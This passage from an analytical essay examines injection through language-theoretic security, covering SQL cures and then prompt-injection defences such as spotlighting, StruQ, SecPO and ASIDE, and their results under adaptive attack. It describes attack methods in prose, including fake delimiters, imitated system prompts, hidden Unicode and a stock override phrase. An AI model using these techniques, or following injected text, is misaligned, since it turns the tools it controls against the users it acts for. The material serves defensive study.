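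Intents can be more flexible than Su and Wassermann's permitted symbols. If an application asks the user for a comparison sign and a number together, such as "> 5", the parse tree may have no node that covers only those two. Su and Wassermann's definition then treats every such input as an attack, while Alata and Gimenez can define the sequence as the intent.

### Which questions a computer can settle

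Alata and Gimenez also define a grammar as intent-secure for an intent if every template that permits the intent is intent-equivalent to it. Developers using such a grammar could not write a vulnerable template for that intent.

The table gives the results for both properties. LR(k) grammars let a parser read input from left to right while looking *k* symbols ahead, and they define the deterministic context-free languages. LR(0) grammars, including the one for LDAP above, need no lookahead. A terminal is a symbol that no rule replaces, such as s.

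| Back end's grammar | Is a given template safe for a given intent? | Is every template safe, with one blank? | Is every template safe, with two or more blanks? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Finite language | Decidable | Decidable | Decidable |
| Regular, infinite | Decidable | Never | Never |
| LR(0), infinite | Decidable | Undecidable | Never |
| LR(k), infinite | Decidable if the intent for each blank is one symbol or consists of terminals; otherwise unknown | Undecidable | Never |
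| Context-free, infinite | Undecidable in general, but decidable if the intents consist of terminals | Undecidable | Never |

The results for single templates are fairly encouraging. Developers mostly want a name or a number in the blank, which is a single terminal, and for those intents the question is decidable even with an arbitrary context-free grammar. It is also decidable for single-symbol intents in LR(k) grammars, where the proof uses Sénizergues's theorem on the equivalence of deterministic languages. However, Alata and Gimenez don't supply practical algorithms.

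The results for whole grammars are much worse. Every infinite regular language has strings with a part that can repeat, so an attacker can supply several copies where the developer expected one. Any language that contains an infinite regular language has the same problem. An ordinary list is enough to cause it, and JSON has lists, so a program that builds JSON by concatenation is also exposed.

This qualifies LangSec's advice to choose the weakest sufficient language. No infinite regular language is intent-secure, but some context-free languages are, at least for templates with one blank. Alata and Gimenez construct them by giving every grammar rule its own opening and closing symbols. A list of three items then looks like `[ a, [ b, <c> ] ]`, and someone who controls one item can't add another without leaving the brackets unbalanced. Alata and Gimenez consider this too cumbersome for mainstream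 programming languages. Removing grammar rules reduces the danger more reliably than moving to a weaker class of language, because removing rules from an unambiguous grammar never adds an unexpected injection.

The word "never" in the table applies to raw input. An application that escapes its inputs correctly may be safe even in a language that is not intent-secure. Intent-equivalence guarantees only that the input has the right syntax, so it does not stop a user from entering somebody else's name, which is still in *E*.

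### Two cures for SQL

Two methods prevent SQL injection without guessing which inputs look dangerous. Both rely on a reference grammar that determines how the database parses a query, and on a place in that grammar for data.

The standard method is the parameterised query, also known as a prepared statement. The programmer writes the query with a placeholder for each value. According to Poll's lecture notes, the database parses this query first, then inserts the values into the parse tree. On the shop's page, the attacker's OR could not become part of the command because the database would already have parsed it, and the whole input would be treated as one card type. The reference grammar is the database's own, so there is no second parser that could interpret the query differently. The data goes in the placeholders, which SQL allows where a value could appear.

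This also sets the method's limits. Some queries need a structure that varies, for example to test whether a name is in a list of unpredictable length. A programmer can also defeat the method by concatenating user input into the query before the database prepares it. To prevent this, Poll proposes requiring the query text to be a constant in the source code, which a type that tracks trust can enforce. Web pages have no equally clean fix, partly because one page may put the same user's text into HTML, a web address and JavaScript, each with its own rules.

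The other method keeps the concatenation and checks its result. Hansen and Patterson (2005), in *Guns and Butter*, advise programmers to validate the whole command instead of the user's input. For a login query, they define a sublanguage of SQL that allows only the query's fixed text and, in the name and password positions, strings with no syntactic structure of their own. A query with any further condition lies outside the sublanguage, so the program rejects it.

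Dejector, a tool from the same year, generates such sublanguages. According to Sassaman and colleagues, it works like this:

1. The developer collects a set of known-good queries.
2. Dejector parses them with the full SQL grammar and discards every rule, and every alternative within a rule, that none of them uses.
3. A parser generator turns the remaining subgrammar into a recognizer.
4. The recognizer accepts a new query only if it has the same structure as a known-good one.

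Step 2 takes some care because SQL grammars typically join conditions with a rule that can apply repeatedly. A subgrammar that keeps this rule for a query with one AND might also accept one with twenty. Sassaman and colleagues note that the subgrammar must distinguish between uses of the same symbol in different parts of the grammar.

Dejector takes its reference grammar and the code that splits a query into tokens directly from the PostgreSQL database. This ties the tool to one revision of PostgreSQL's parser, but a validator with its own SQL parser risks a parser differential. In 2006, for example, PostgreSQL had a flaw in its handling of characters that occupy several bytes. A validator that assumed one byte per character could accept a query in which the server treated a quoted value as ending early.

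Dejector allows data wherever a known-good query has a value, so its protection is only as good as its collection of queries. Hansen and Patterson warn that programmers can define sublanguages that don't meet their own security expectations, and that no general procedure can detect this. Combining many queries in one recognizer adds another risk. Alata and Gimenez show that the union of two intent-secure languages can fail to be intent-secure. Even if every accepted query shape is harmless where the developer meant to use it, an input might still turn one accepted query into another.

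Both methods help least when users are supposed to write part of the query. Su and Wassermann note that placeholders can't hold the stored search conditions that Bugzilla needs, because a placeholder only takes a value. A grammar can still restrict the user to writing a condition and block commands that change the database. Within that condition, however, the user's text is meant to control what the database does, and no position is reserved for data alone.

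## Whether a prompt has an input language that can be checked

A prompt, like an SQL query built by concatenation, combines a developer's text with a stranger's, so it seems natural to look for a grammar in prompts too. A developer following LangSec would define the language of acceptable prompts and put a recognizer in front of the model to reject everything else.

### A recognizer that rejects nothing

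A language model computes a next token for any sequence of tokens that fits in its context window, so no prompt that fits is a syntax error. The language the model accepts is the set of all token strings up to a certain length, and a recognizer for it only has to count tokens. This language is finite and therefore regular, and two programs that enforce the same limit can't disagree about which prompts are valid. Prompts can still be unsafe, so a simple input language isn't enough to make a program safe.

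The LangSec premise that input is a program holds unusually well for prompts. Schuurmans (2023), in *Memory Augmented Large Language Models are Computationally Universal*, wrote fifteen prompts that made Flan-U-PaLM 540B act as the processor of a general-purpose computer without changing its weights. An email in plain English can likewise determine which tool a mail assistant calls next.

The premise that a component must reject everything outside its intended language helps much less. The assistant's designer wants it to read whatever arrives in the inbox, so the intended language for that part of the prompt is roughly any text an email can contain. That language includes emails with injections, so even a perfect recognizer would accept them.

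Recognizers can still block some tricks. Von Hippel and Miyazono cite an attack called the Rules File Backdoor, in which invisible Unicode characters in a configuration file lead an AI system to write malicious code. They see it as a difference between how the human and the machine read the file, which makes it a kind of parser differential. A finite automaton could enforce a ban on invisible characters. *Don't say "Jehova" to an LLM* (2025), an article from Austria's computer emergency response team, CERT.at, lists similar tricks, such as white text on a white background and images whose instructions appear only after software shrinks them. But an attacker can also write the instruction in ordinary visible words.

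### What the definition of injection gives

Alata and Gimenez's test for a template requires *F* (the strings that fit the blank) to equal *E* (the strings the developer intends), and it also applies to a prompt. If the receiver's language contains every string, *F* does too, because anything fits the blank. The prompt then fails the test if the developer intends anything narrower than "any text at all", such as a name or a question about a meeting, however the text around the blank is worded. The context window limit only reduces *F* to every string that fits in the remaining space. This is not a new result, since Alata and Gimenez's theorem that every infinite regular language is insecure already covers the set of all strings.

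A developer could instead declare that the intent is any text. Then *E* equals *F* and the template counts as safe, even though the recruiter's system from the first section would still follow the hidden instructions in the CV. Every prompt template therefore counts as either unsafe or safe depending on the declared intent, and the definition does not distinguish an honest CV from a malicious one in either case.

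This happens because Alata and Gimenez assume that the parse tree of a language's reference grammar closely tracks meaning, instead of modelling meaning directly. That assumption is reasonable for SQL because the database acts on that tree. Linguists have written grammars for English too, but a language model doesn't execute their parse trees, so there is no node at which the CV would count only as data.

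### One channel for instructions and data

Engineers have dealt before with channels that carry both instructions and data. CERT.at compares the prompt to the telephone network that callers could control by imitating its tones, and to computer memory, which holds programs and their data as the same kind of bits. The lasting fixes gave the receiver a rule that it enforces whatever the data contains. A processor can block execution of memory that the operating system has marked as data, and prepared statements give databases a similar rule. CERT.at has seen no equivalent of the prepared statement for prompts, and asks whether anyone has formally defined how quotation should work in them.

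The article also describes a chief executive who forwarded a phishing email to a secretary with the words "please handle this". The executive wanted the secretary to check whether the email was genuine, but the secretary followed the email's instructions. People usually resolve such ambiguities from context, and an agent has to do the same.

David C thinks the comparison with SQL injection is dangerous because it suggests that a similar fix exists. In SQL, the database engine carries out instructions and stores or uses data, so a parameterised query enforces an existing distinction. In David C's view, detecting injections, training models to prioritise instructions and marking which text is data are all attempts to add that distinction to a technology that lacks it.

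Pant, Lohani and Kumar (2026), in *On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models*, try to turn the single-channel argument into a theorem. They consider models with three features:

- Trusted and untrusted text go through the same computation.
- The architecture has no barrier between them that a user can't forge or bypass.
- Decisions such as whether to call a tool come out of that shared computation.

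Inside a model, a list of numbers called a vector represents each token. Suppose someone sees one such vector and has to guess whether the developer or a stranger supplied the token. If both are equally likely beforehand, the best possible guesser is wrong with probability

½ (1 − TV)

where TV, the total variation distance, measures how far apart the two distributions of vectors are. It is 0 if they are identical and 1 if they never overlap. The word "the" enters the model as the same vector whoever wrote it, so TV is less than 1 at that point and some error is unavoidable.

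This part of the argument shows less than it seems to. Deeper in the model, a token's vector also reflects its context, and Pant and colleagues assume, but do not prove, that the distributions overlap there. The system prompt also usually comes first, so a token's position may reveal its source. A model may well have enough information to tell the sources apart, but nothing forces it to use that information.

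The rest of the proof concerns a property that Pant and colleagues call Semantic-Faithful Control. It requires a model to make the same decisions about tools and refusals for any two untrusted inputs with the same meaning, even if one is in plain text and the other in an encoding such as base64. Training on finitely many examples can't guarantee this for infinitely many encodings. But a model that followed every untrusted instruction in every encoding would have the property. A harmless model would lack it if it called a decoding tool only for base64 text. The theorem therefore doesn't quite establish the paper's larger claim that such models can't perfectly prevent prompt injection.

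Pant and colleagues also list designs their theorem doesn't cover. A model could process trusted and untrusted text in separate encoders, or block untrusted text from reaching the computations that make decisions. A developer could also leave the model unchanged and have separate software authorize its tool calls.

### The confused deputy

David C proposes treating a language model as an "inherently confusable deputy" rather than a victim of code injection. The term derives from Hardy's *The Confused Deputy*, which recounts a "nearly true" incident at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers.

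Tymshare's compiler kept usage statistics in a file in its own directory, and the operating system gave the compiler permission to write there. Users could also name a file to receive debugging output. One user named the company's billing file, which was in the same directory. The operating system let the compiler open that file because the compiler had permission to write in the directory, and the debugging output overwrote the billing records.

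The compiler was a deputy because it acted for others, and it was confused because it held authority from two sources and couldn't indicate which one it was using. It should have written the statistics with its own authority and the debugging output with the user's. Input checking would have been a poor remedy because the billing file's name was a valid file name. Hardy asks whether the programmers would have to change the compiler every time someone added a sensitive file to the directory. His solution is a capability, a reference that both identifies a file and grants permission to use it. The user had no capability for the billing file, so they couldn't have given one to the compiler.

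The mail assistant is in a similar position. It has the user's authority to send email, and a stranger's message can determine what it uses that authority for. However, the compiler opened its two files at separate places in its code, and a programmer could attach a different authority to each. A language model has no such separate places, because all the text in its context window can influence the computation that produces each tool call. This seems to be the best reason for David C's use of the word "inherently".

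Developers can still limit the deputy's authority from outside. David C advises them to assume that an attacker can use any tool the model can, and to rely on deterministic safeguards, meaning ordinary software that limits what the system can do. He also repeats a rule from an online discussion between Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista that a model processing a party's information should have no more privileges than that party. The rule is simple, but applied strictly, it would stop the assistant from answering Dana at all, since Dana has no right to send email from the user's account.

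### Input and output

Von Hippel and Miyazono claim that AI security is inherently a language-theoretic problem. Their claim concerns the model's output, so it does not contradict David C's position on the input. They want developers to formalize a system's goals and check the formalization against the text that the model generates.

They compare this with two other ways of controlling AI systems. The first is alignment, which means getting the system to understand what people want and decide accordingly. They doubt that the leading labs will achieve it in time. The second is human review, which they expect to become infeasible as the volume and complexity of output grow. Structured outputs and tool calls suit formal checking because ordinary programs read them. Developers tend to write the parsers for structured outputs piecemeal and run them alongside the main application, so an attacker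 who can influence the model's output can use it to exploit a flaw in the parser.

Prompt injection can also lead to SQL injection if a database tool runs whatever SQL the model writes. Von Hippel and Miyazono propose restricting the tool to a safe sublanguage of SQL, much as Dejector does for web applications. They also propose enforcing policies on tools, for example that a database tool never deletes data or that a weather tool makes at most 100 queries a second.

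Von Hippel and Miyazono offer little evidence. Besides the traffic figures from Maitai, they surveyed five founders of startups backed by the investment firm Y Combinator, and they call the results anecdotal. Four of the founders used structured outputs or special-purpose languages, one had developed a custom parser, and four expressed security concerns. The slides describe Maitai's shares of requests as shares of "AI products", which the data can't support. The figures show that some companies use these features, but they don't measure how often attackers exploit them, and the paper's table of tool exploits is explicitly theoretical.

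The argument for checking outputs holds without more data, since a parser or database at that interface uses a grammar. It does not affect David C's claim about inputs. The model is like a web application between a user and a database, in that a stranger's text enters without any useful grammar and may leave as a well-formed command. Von Hippel and Miyazono overstate their case if "inherently" is meant to cover the security of the whole agent. A recognizer for `send_email` calls can establish that the recipient is an email address, but not that the user wanted to write to that person.

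### Is the question undecidable?

O'Connor (2026) argues in *CBCL* for a restricted language between agents, partly because judging whether an arbitrary natural-language message will cause harm "requires solving undecidable problems". The paper does not prove this. O'Connor does class language-model agents as recursively enumerable, the one class where membership is undecidable, but explains in a note that the label describes the whole process of interpreting a message, including tools that may run arbitrary code, and not the syntax alone.

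Without such tools the claim is false. If the model's weights, the text around the message, the rule for picking tokens and the maximum length of the reply are all fixed, anyone can find out what the message makes the model write by running it once, and the run always ends. If harm means that the reply contains a particular tool call, then whether a message is harmful is decidable, and checking a single message takes little compute.

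Checking every possible message is another matter. With a vocabulary of 100,000 tokens and 1,000 positions to fill, there are

100,000^1,000 = 10^5,000

strings to try. A window of 100,000 tokens raises the exponent to 500,000. The search is finite, so the question remains decidable in principle, but no computer could complete it.

Faster methods than brute force may exist, but they have limits too. *Transformer Encoder Satisfiability* (Sälzer, Alsmann and Lange, 2024) examines the problem of deciding whether any input leads a given transformer encoder to a particular output. An encoder here is a model that classifies text instead of generating it. The problem is undecidable for an idealized class of encoders. It becomes decidable if either the length of the input or the precision of the arithmetic is limited, and real computers limit both. Even then, the length-limited problem is NP-hard,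 and the worst cases with limited precision take exponential time. These results apply to whole classes of encoders, so a particular model might be easier to check.

Detecting adversarial prompts can also take more computation than a filter has available. In *On the Impossibility of Separating Intelligence from Judgment*, Ball, Gluch and colleagues (2025) construct language models for which, under standard cryptographic assumptions, no efficient filter can distinguish adversarial prompts from benign ones. They build these models specially and study prompts that elicit harmful content, so the result doesn't show that every filter for a deployed agent must fail.

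An agent with external memory can escape the limits of a single run. Schuurmans notes that a deterministic model reading strings of bounded length is equivalent to a finite automaton, and then adds a memory that can grow:

1. Software fetches a prompt from memory and inserts stored values into it.
2. The model completes the prompt.
3. A simple pattern matcher finds assignments in the output and stores them, including the choice of the next prompt.
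4. The cycle repeats until the next prompt is "halt".

Schuurmans shows that this system exactly simulates a universal Turing machine, which can carry out any computation. No general procedure can therefore predict whether the system will stop. According to *Autoregressive Large Language Models are Computationally Universal* (2024), a model can do the same without external memory if it may generate text indefinitely. The storage must therefore be unlimited, but it can be inside or outside the model.

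O'Connor's description fits an agent that can run code with unlimited time and storage. But a tool that accepted programs in a language with a very simple grammar would raise the same problem, so natural language isn't the cause. *LLM Censorship* (Glukhov, Shumailov and colleagues, 2023) had already made the argument for model outputs that describe programs, using Rice's theorem, which implies that no procedure can decide a nontrivial property of what arbitrary programs compute. Real agents also run out of time, storage or money, and whether an agent does something harmful within a fixed number of steps is decidable by running it for that many steps.

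Amer, Kinczel and Long (2026) prove in *No Perfect Guardrail & No Perfect Guard* that judging messages is undecidable if the recipient can carry out any program exactly, with unlimited time and memory. They warn that an agent isn't such a recipient merely because it reads documents, and that saying an agent is susceptible to prompt injection is a different claim.

Preventing a program from doing harm may be easy even when nobody can predict what it will do. Amer and colleagues describe a monitor that stops a program just before it takes any action on a list of harmful ones. The monitor makes no mistakes if it sees every action and can stop each one. It could ensure that the mail assistant never deletes a message. But before it could stop the assistant from sending email on a stranger's behalf, someone would have to define which calls do that.

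### A missing specification

Even if a computer could run the model on all 10^5,000 prompts and list the resulting tool calls, somebody would still have to decide which calls were wrong. Amer and colleagues point out that a policy becomes a definite set only when someone specifies it.

For prompt injection, a specification of that set has to relate the text to the user's task and to the action that follows. If Dana's email asks for the meeting's agenda and the user has told the assistant to deal with Dana's requests, sending the agenda is part of the task. If the user only wanted a summary of the inbox and the assistant sends the agenda, the email has made it depart from its task. The email is identical in both cases, so a set of texts can't distinguish them.

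Classifiers that look for typical attack phrases avoid this problem by solving a simpler one. *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections* (2026) reports a test on 8,400 emails, with paired versions that differed only in one clause. In one version of each pair the clause asserted authority, and neither version used phrases like "ignore all instructions". Meta's classifier Prompt Guard 2 scored 0.59 at telling the versions apart, on a scale where 0.5 is chance and 1 is perfect. The low score isn't surprising, because Prompt Guard 2 looks for more obvious attacks, but it shows that such a classifier can contribute little when the danger depends on who is entitled to ask for what.

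Researchers haven't agreed on a better definition. The organisers of *Foundations of Language Model Security*, a workshop at the machine-learning conference NeurIPS, write that the field lacks shared formal definitions comparable to differential privacy, the standard mathematical measure of how much a computation reveals about any one person. They also leave open whether the lack of separation between instructions and data is inherent to current language models or results from particular designs.

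One classical candidate is noninterference, which requires that nothing an attacker observes depends on the user's secrets. Dongol (2026), in *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection*, considers this too strict. For example, a calendar assistant meant to answer meeting requests with the user's availability would violate it. Developers can allow exceptions, but then they have to write a release policy for each task.

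Dongol instead compares the agent with a reference agent that follows the same plan under the same monitor, but whose model never follows instructions in untrusted text. The real agent is secure if an attacker can't use an injection to learn anything about the user's data that the reference agent wouldn't also reveal. If a stranger's email tells the calendar assistant to send the user's calendar and it does, this isn't a leak under the definition, because a genuine meeting request would have produced the same reply. An email would cause a leak if it obtained a password-reset code that the plan never sends. Dongol used a proof assistant to prove or refute security for 25 small example agents.

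The definition covers only leaks, so an injection that made an agent delete a message without revealing anything would not violate it. It also needs a plan fixed before the agent reads any untrusted text, because the plan serves as the specification. The mail assistant's model chooses each call after reading the results of the last one, so a reference agent would have no plan to follow. Dongol excludes agents like the mail assistant for this reason.

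## Marking data apart from instructions inside the model

Dongol's definition compares a real agent with one whose model never follows instructions in untrusted text. Nobody has built such a model, but since 2024 several research groups have tried to approximate one by marking which parts of a prompt are data and training the model not to follow instructions in those parts. They want untrusted text to have a place in the prompt where it can't act as a command, like a parameter in a parameterised database query.

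### Spotlighting

The simplest method does not change the model. *Defending Against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks With Spotlighting* (Hines, Lopez and colleagues, 2024) describes three ways for an application to mark untrusted text. In each case, the system prompt explains the mark and tells the model not to follow any instructions in the marked text.

- Delimiting puts one symbol before the text and another after it.
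- Datamarking puts a special character between the words, so the mark runs through the whole text.
- Encoding converts the text into a code such as base64, which capable models can read directly.

Hines and colleagues tested these methods on 1,000 synthetic documents, each with an injected instruction to reply with a single keyword. Without a defence, GPT-3.5 Turbo followed the injection more than half the time when asked to summarise the documents. Delimiters roughly halved the rate, datamarking cut it to 3.1%, and encoding cut it to zero. However, encoding the text made GPT-3.5 Turbo much worse at ordinary tasks, though GPT-4 still performed well.

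An attacker who learns the delimiter can write it into the document, so Hines and colleagues advise against plain delimiting. For datamarking, they suggest a new random marker for each request. Five characters from an alphabet of 50 would give 50^5, or about 310 million, possible markers. SQLCheck also relied on unguessable markers, but its parser blocked any query in which an input went beyond its permitted syntactic role. Spotlighting depends entirely on the model following the system prompt's instructions about the marker, so an attacker may not need to guess it.

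The method may also work for a different reason than its designers intended. *Lessons from Defending Gemini Against Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) describes a version for Google's Gemini models that inserts a marker after every eight characters of an email. This version worked mainly by breaking up the tokens of the attack text, which made Gemini less likely to react to the injection. That effect is closer to garbling the command than to separating data from instructions.

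### Markers that outside text can't contain

Chen, Piet and colleagues (2024), in *StruQ*, changed both the format of the prompt and the model. In their system, the application supplies the instruction and the data separately, and a program called the front end combines them:

1. It labels the instruction, the data and the space for the reply with reserved tokens, which have no other use.
2. It deletes any text in the data that would turn into a reserved token.
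3. It repeats the deletion until nothing changes, because removing one marker can join the two halves of another.
4. It sends the result to a model that Chen and colleagues have trained on this format.

The first three steps guarantee that the data part contains no reserved token, whatever a stranger writes, and a developer can verify this without running the model. The texts that avoid a few fixed strings form a regular language, and a simple parser can always find where the data begins and ends. If the developer's declared intent is "any text without reserved tokens", every input that leaves the filter matches it, and no injection remains in Alata and Gimenez's sense.

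That would be enough in a database, but a language model processes the reserved tokens in the same computation as the rest of its input, and its response to them depends on its training. The fourth step is therefore not guaranteed.

Chen and colleagues trained two open models, Llama-7B and Mistral-7B. They left half the training examples unchanged. In the other half, wherever an example came with data, they added a second instruction to the data, sometimes after a fake reply and fake delimiters. The correct answer still responded only to the first instruction.

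They then tested whether injections could make the models print a fixed word. The best handwritten attacks copied the real delimiters and worked 96% of the time on undefended models, but no handwritten attack exceeded 2% against StruQ. An automated attack that uses a language model to tailor the injection to each task succeeded against StruQ in 9% of cases on Llama and 36% on Mistral. Another automated attack, which requires access to the model's weights, succeeded in more than half. StruQ hardly changed the quality of the models' ordinary answers.

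The front end also deletes double hash marks, which are not reserved, because Chen and colleagues found that attackers could use them in place of the real marker with some success. A filter can be guaranteed to remove every copy of a reserved token, but that may not stop an attack, because nobody can list every other text that a model might treat the same way.

The same gap exists in current chat formats. Chen, Peng and colleagues (2026) explain in *SecPO* that a well-written library, such as OpenAI's Harmony, can ensure that no message escapes its assigned role. An attacker can still use fake delimiters or fake replies to trick the model into treating data as a trusted prompt.

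### Training on good and bad replies

StruQ's training examples contain only the right reply. SecAlign and its successor, Meta-SecAlign, use preference training, which also shows the model a wrong one. According to Chen and colleagues' account in *SecPO*, Meta-SecAlign's developers build each example as follows:

1. They take a request with its data and insert an unrelated instruction at the beginning or end of the data.
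2. The undefended model answers the original request without the injection. This is the good reply.
3. The undefended model answers the inserted instruction alone. This is the bad reply.
4. They train the model to favour the good reply when it receives the prompt with the injection.

Let *R* be the probability of the good reply divided by that of the bad one, given the injected prompt. Let *R*₀ be the same ratio for the undefended model. Training minimises

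−log σ(β log(*R*/*R*₀))

where σ(*x*) = 1/(1 + e^(−*x*)) and β is a constant, 0.1 in Chen and colleagues' experiments. The loss falls as *R* rises above *R*₀. Comparing the two models keeps the trained one from drifting too far from the original and losing its general abilities.

### A different vector for data

Hines and colleagues wanted a separate channel for instructions, as in modern telephone networks, but saw no straightforward way to build one into the language models of 2024. *ASIDE* (Zverev, Kortukov and colleagues, 2025) comes closer to such a channel. Pant and colleagues' impossibility argument assumes that a word enters the model as the same vector whoever wrote it, and this assumption doesn't hold for ASIDE.

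ASIDE splits the vector of each data token into pairs of numbers and rotates each pair by 90 degrees, so that (*a*, *b*) becomes (−*b*, *a*). Instruction tokens keep their usual vectors. The application chooses which tokens to rotate based on where the text came from, so an attacker has no marker to forge. The rotation adds no parameters, and developers can add it to an existing model and fine-tune the model to use it.

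Zverev and colleagues measured how well models separate instructions from data by placing an extra instruction in either the instruction part or the data part of the prompt. A model scores well if it carries out the extra instruction only when it appears in the instruction part. ASIDE raised scores by 12.3 percentage points (Llama 2 7B) to 44.1 points (Mistral 7B), compared with the same models trained with ordinary delimiters.

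Injections also became less successful, even though the training data contained no attacks. The average success rate across models fell from 14.7% to 4.9% on one benchmark, but only from 45% to 36% on another. Both benchmarks used fixed attacks, so a determined attacker would probably succeed more often.

With ASIDE, the models still followed the remaining 36% of injections, even though the vectors distinguish data from instructions from the first layer onward. The models therefore had information about the source but didn't reliably use it.

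### Ranked sources

An agent has to separate more than two kinds of text. Chen and colleagues' StruQ paper describes OpenAI's instruction hierarchy, also from 2024, as a generalisation of StruQ to several levels. OpenAI deployed the hierarchy in GPT-4o mini. *When Context Gets Root* (2026) puts the message types of OpenAI, Anthropic and Google in one ranking, with system prompts at the top, user messages below them and tool results at the bottom. A tool result keeps its low rank even if it is sent in a message with the user role, as in Anthropic's format.

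OpenAI calls the ranking a "chain of command" in its Model Spec, a document on how its models should behave. As *Prompt Governance?* (2026) explains, model providers typically put some of their own rules above the developer's system prompt, so that neither developers nor users can override them.

*Many-Tier Instruction Hierarchy in LLM Agents* (2026) argues that agents need more than a few fixed privilege levels. It proposes giving each instruction its own privilege number, even when several instructions appear in the same message, and telling the model at the start of the prompt how to resolve conflicts. For example, an instruction with privilege 82 from a developer's configuration file would override conflicting instructions with privileges 61 and 40. The agent's software can assign the numbers based on each text's source.

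Such numbers need the same protection as StruQ's markers, since outside text could otherwise include a high number. *IH-Challenge* (2026), which presents a dataset for training models to respect instruction rankings, includes an example in which text presented as a very high-priority system instruction requests a secret PIN from the real system message. Only training can keep the model from acting on such a false claim, although software can stop outside text from acquiring a genuine rank.

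A ranking also resolves only conflicts between instructions. If the user asks for a summary of the inbox and an email asks for a copy of the agenda, the assistant could do both without disobeying anyone. The ranking therefore needs an added rule that tool results can't start new tasks, but that rule would be too strict for a user who wants the assistant to deal with Dana's requests.

### Twelve defences under adaptive attack

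Most of these defences looked strong in their developers' own tests. In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) retested twelve defences with adaptive attacks, which are designed with knowledge of the defence. Their automated attacks repeatedly proposed candidate texts, scored the target's responses and kept the most promising candidates. They also held an online competition with more than 500 participants.

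Two of the twelve defences mainly address jailbreaks, and attacks on them succeeded at least 96% of the time. The table shows the results of the automated attacks on the other ten.

| Defence | Method | Success of adaptive attacks |
|---|---|---|
| Spotlighting | Marks text by its source | Above 95% |
| Prompt Sandwiching | Repeats the user's request after the untrusted text | Above 95% |
| StruQ | Reserved tokens and training | Every case tested |
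| Meta-SecAlign | Preference training | 96% |
| Protect AI, PromptGuard and Model Armor | Separate classifiers that look for attacks | Above 90% |
| PIGuard | Separate classifier | 71% |
| Data Sentinel | Checks whether the text distracts a model from a dummy task | Every case tested |
| MELON | Runs the agent again without the user's request and compares the tool calls | 76%, or 95% if the attacker knows the defence |

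Fixed attacks succeeded far less often on AgentDojo, a benchmark for agents that use tools. Their success rate was as little as 1% against spotlighting and Prompt Sandwiching, and Meta-SecAlign's developers had reported a 2% success rate against it. On a selected set of scenarios, the automated search succeeded in 69%, while the human participants collectively succeeded in all of them.

Most of the successful attacks against the trained defences imitated a system prompt. An imitation in ordinary words contains no reserved token, so StruQ's filter does not remove it. Even when the filter works perfectly, the model can still follow the injected instructions despite its training.

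The percentages can't be used to rank the defences, because Nasr and colleagues used different benchmarks and attacks for different systems. Their description of spotlighting also suggests that they tested delimiters, the version Hines and colleagues had advised against, so the result may not apply to datamarking or encoding. They gave the attacker a lot of computing power and, for the classifiers, feedback on how confident each one was. A stranger who sends a single email to the mail assistant gets no such feedback, but a defence is still weak if it works only against attackers who haven't practised.

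### Training against stronger attacks

Chen and colleagues developed SecPO in response to Meta-SecAlign's failure, which they attribute to two faults in its training. The first is the comparison with the undefended model, which often assigns the bad reply a higher probability than the good one on an injected prompt, so *R*₀ sets a low standard.

They derive a better standard from an imaginary ideal model. It would ignore injections, so its replies to an injected prompt would have the same probabilities as its replies to the clean prompt. It would also lose none of the original model's abilities, so on the clean prompt it would behave exactly like the undefended model. Together these requirements give

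ideal(reply | injected prompt) = undefended(reply | clean prompt)

The ideal model doesn't exist, but the researchers add the injections themselves, so they always have the clean prompt. They can therefore calculate the right-hand side and use it in place of Meta-SecAlign's comparison. In the formula, *R*₀ becomes the undefended model's ratio on the clean prompt.

Suppose the undefended model is ten times as likely to give the bad reply as the good one when the prompt contains the injection, but a million times as likely to give the good reply when it doesn't. Partway through training, the new model is 100 times as likely to give the good reply as the bad one on the injected prompt. Meta-SecAlign compares this with the undefended model's ratio on the same prompt, which the new model beats by a factor of 1,000. SecPO compares it with the undefended model's ratio without the injection, and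 the new model falls short of that by a factor of 10,000. With β = 0.1, SecPO would give this example slightly more than twice as much weight in the next training step as Meta-SecAlign would. SecPO concentrates on the examples in which the injection most changed the undefended model's behaviour.

The second fault is that Meta-SecAlign trains on weak, fixed attacks. SecPO instead has another language model propose eight injections at a time for each example, over 30 rounds. A third model scores the results, and the best of the 240 attempts goes into the training data. This took 18 hours on 16 high-end processors for Llama-3.1-8B-Instruct. Chen and colleagues then reused the injections to train a larger model, Qwen3.6-27B, whose results are given below.

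| Adaptive attack | Attempts per task | Undefended | Meta-SecAlign | SecPO |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Genetic search, single requests | 800 | 100% | 93.7% | 13.3% |
| Tree search, single requests | 800 | 100% | 90.1% | 12.5% |
| Attacker trained by reinforcement learning, single requests | 10 | 98.1% | 94.0% | 1.8% |
| Genetic search, AgentDojo | 800 | 81.3% | 78.8% | 8.8% |

A task counts as broken if any of the attempts succeeds. The paper's headline comparison, a maximum of 13.3% for SecPO against 94.0% for Meta-SecAlign, uses figures from two different attacks, but the improvement is large in every row. The attacks also differ from the one SecPO uses in training. The AgentDojo sample has only 80 tasks, so 8.8% means seven broken tasks. Most of the improvement against the first attack came from the new standard of comparison, since stronger training attacks alone reduced the rate from 93.7%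 to 60.9%.

The defence had little effect on the model's usefulness. With it, Qwen3.6-27B averaged 89.1% on six benchmarks of instruction following, science and mathematics, compared with 88.9% before. Agent tasks are a harder test, because a model that ignores data too readily may miss information it needs. Wang and colleagues found that many defences score well on existing benchmarks because they make the agent ignore its environment, and then fail on tasks that depend on it. AgentDyn has 60 tasks in which the data should change the agent's next action. The model completed 71.7% of them both with and without the defence.

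Chen and colleagues trained and tested the model only with its step-by-step reasoning switched off. They also assume that the application correctly labels all untrusted text, and they exclude cases where the agent should follow an instruction in the data because it fits the user's request. The training rewards replies that leave out the injected content, so a mail assistant trained this way might omit Dana's request for the agenda from a summary that should mention it.

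The attacks that still work are subtle. In DTaP, a set of 1,838 simulated agent tasks, 140 injections succeeded, and in 75 of those cases the model also completed the user's task. One user asked for a repair to a Python installation. A project file presented an unrelated piece of insecure code as a requirement, and the model wrote and ran that code along with the repair. The average cost of a successful attack on AgentDojo rose from $5.92 to $34.90, which is still low for an attacker seeking someone's confidential mail.

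### Injection rates of leading models

AI companies publish some success rates for prompt injection attacks in system cards, the reports that accompany new models. According to Digital Applied (2026), a firm that reviewed the card for Anthropic's Claude Fable 5, adaptive attacks on coding tasks had a success rate of 0.41%, down from 2.09% for Claude Opus 4.8. The tests allowed 200 attempts per scenario.

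A rate like this means very different things depending on whether it counts scenarios or single attempts. If 0.41% were the chance for each attempt, and the attempts were independent, the chance of at least one success in 200 would be

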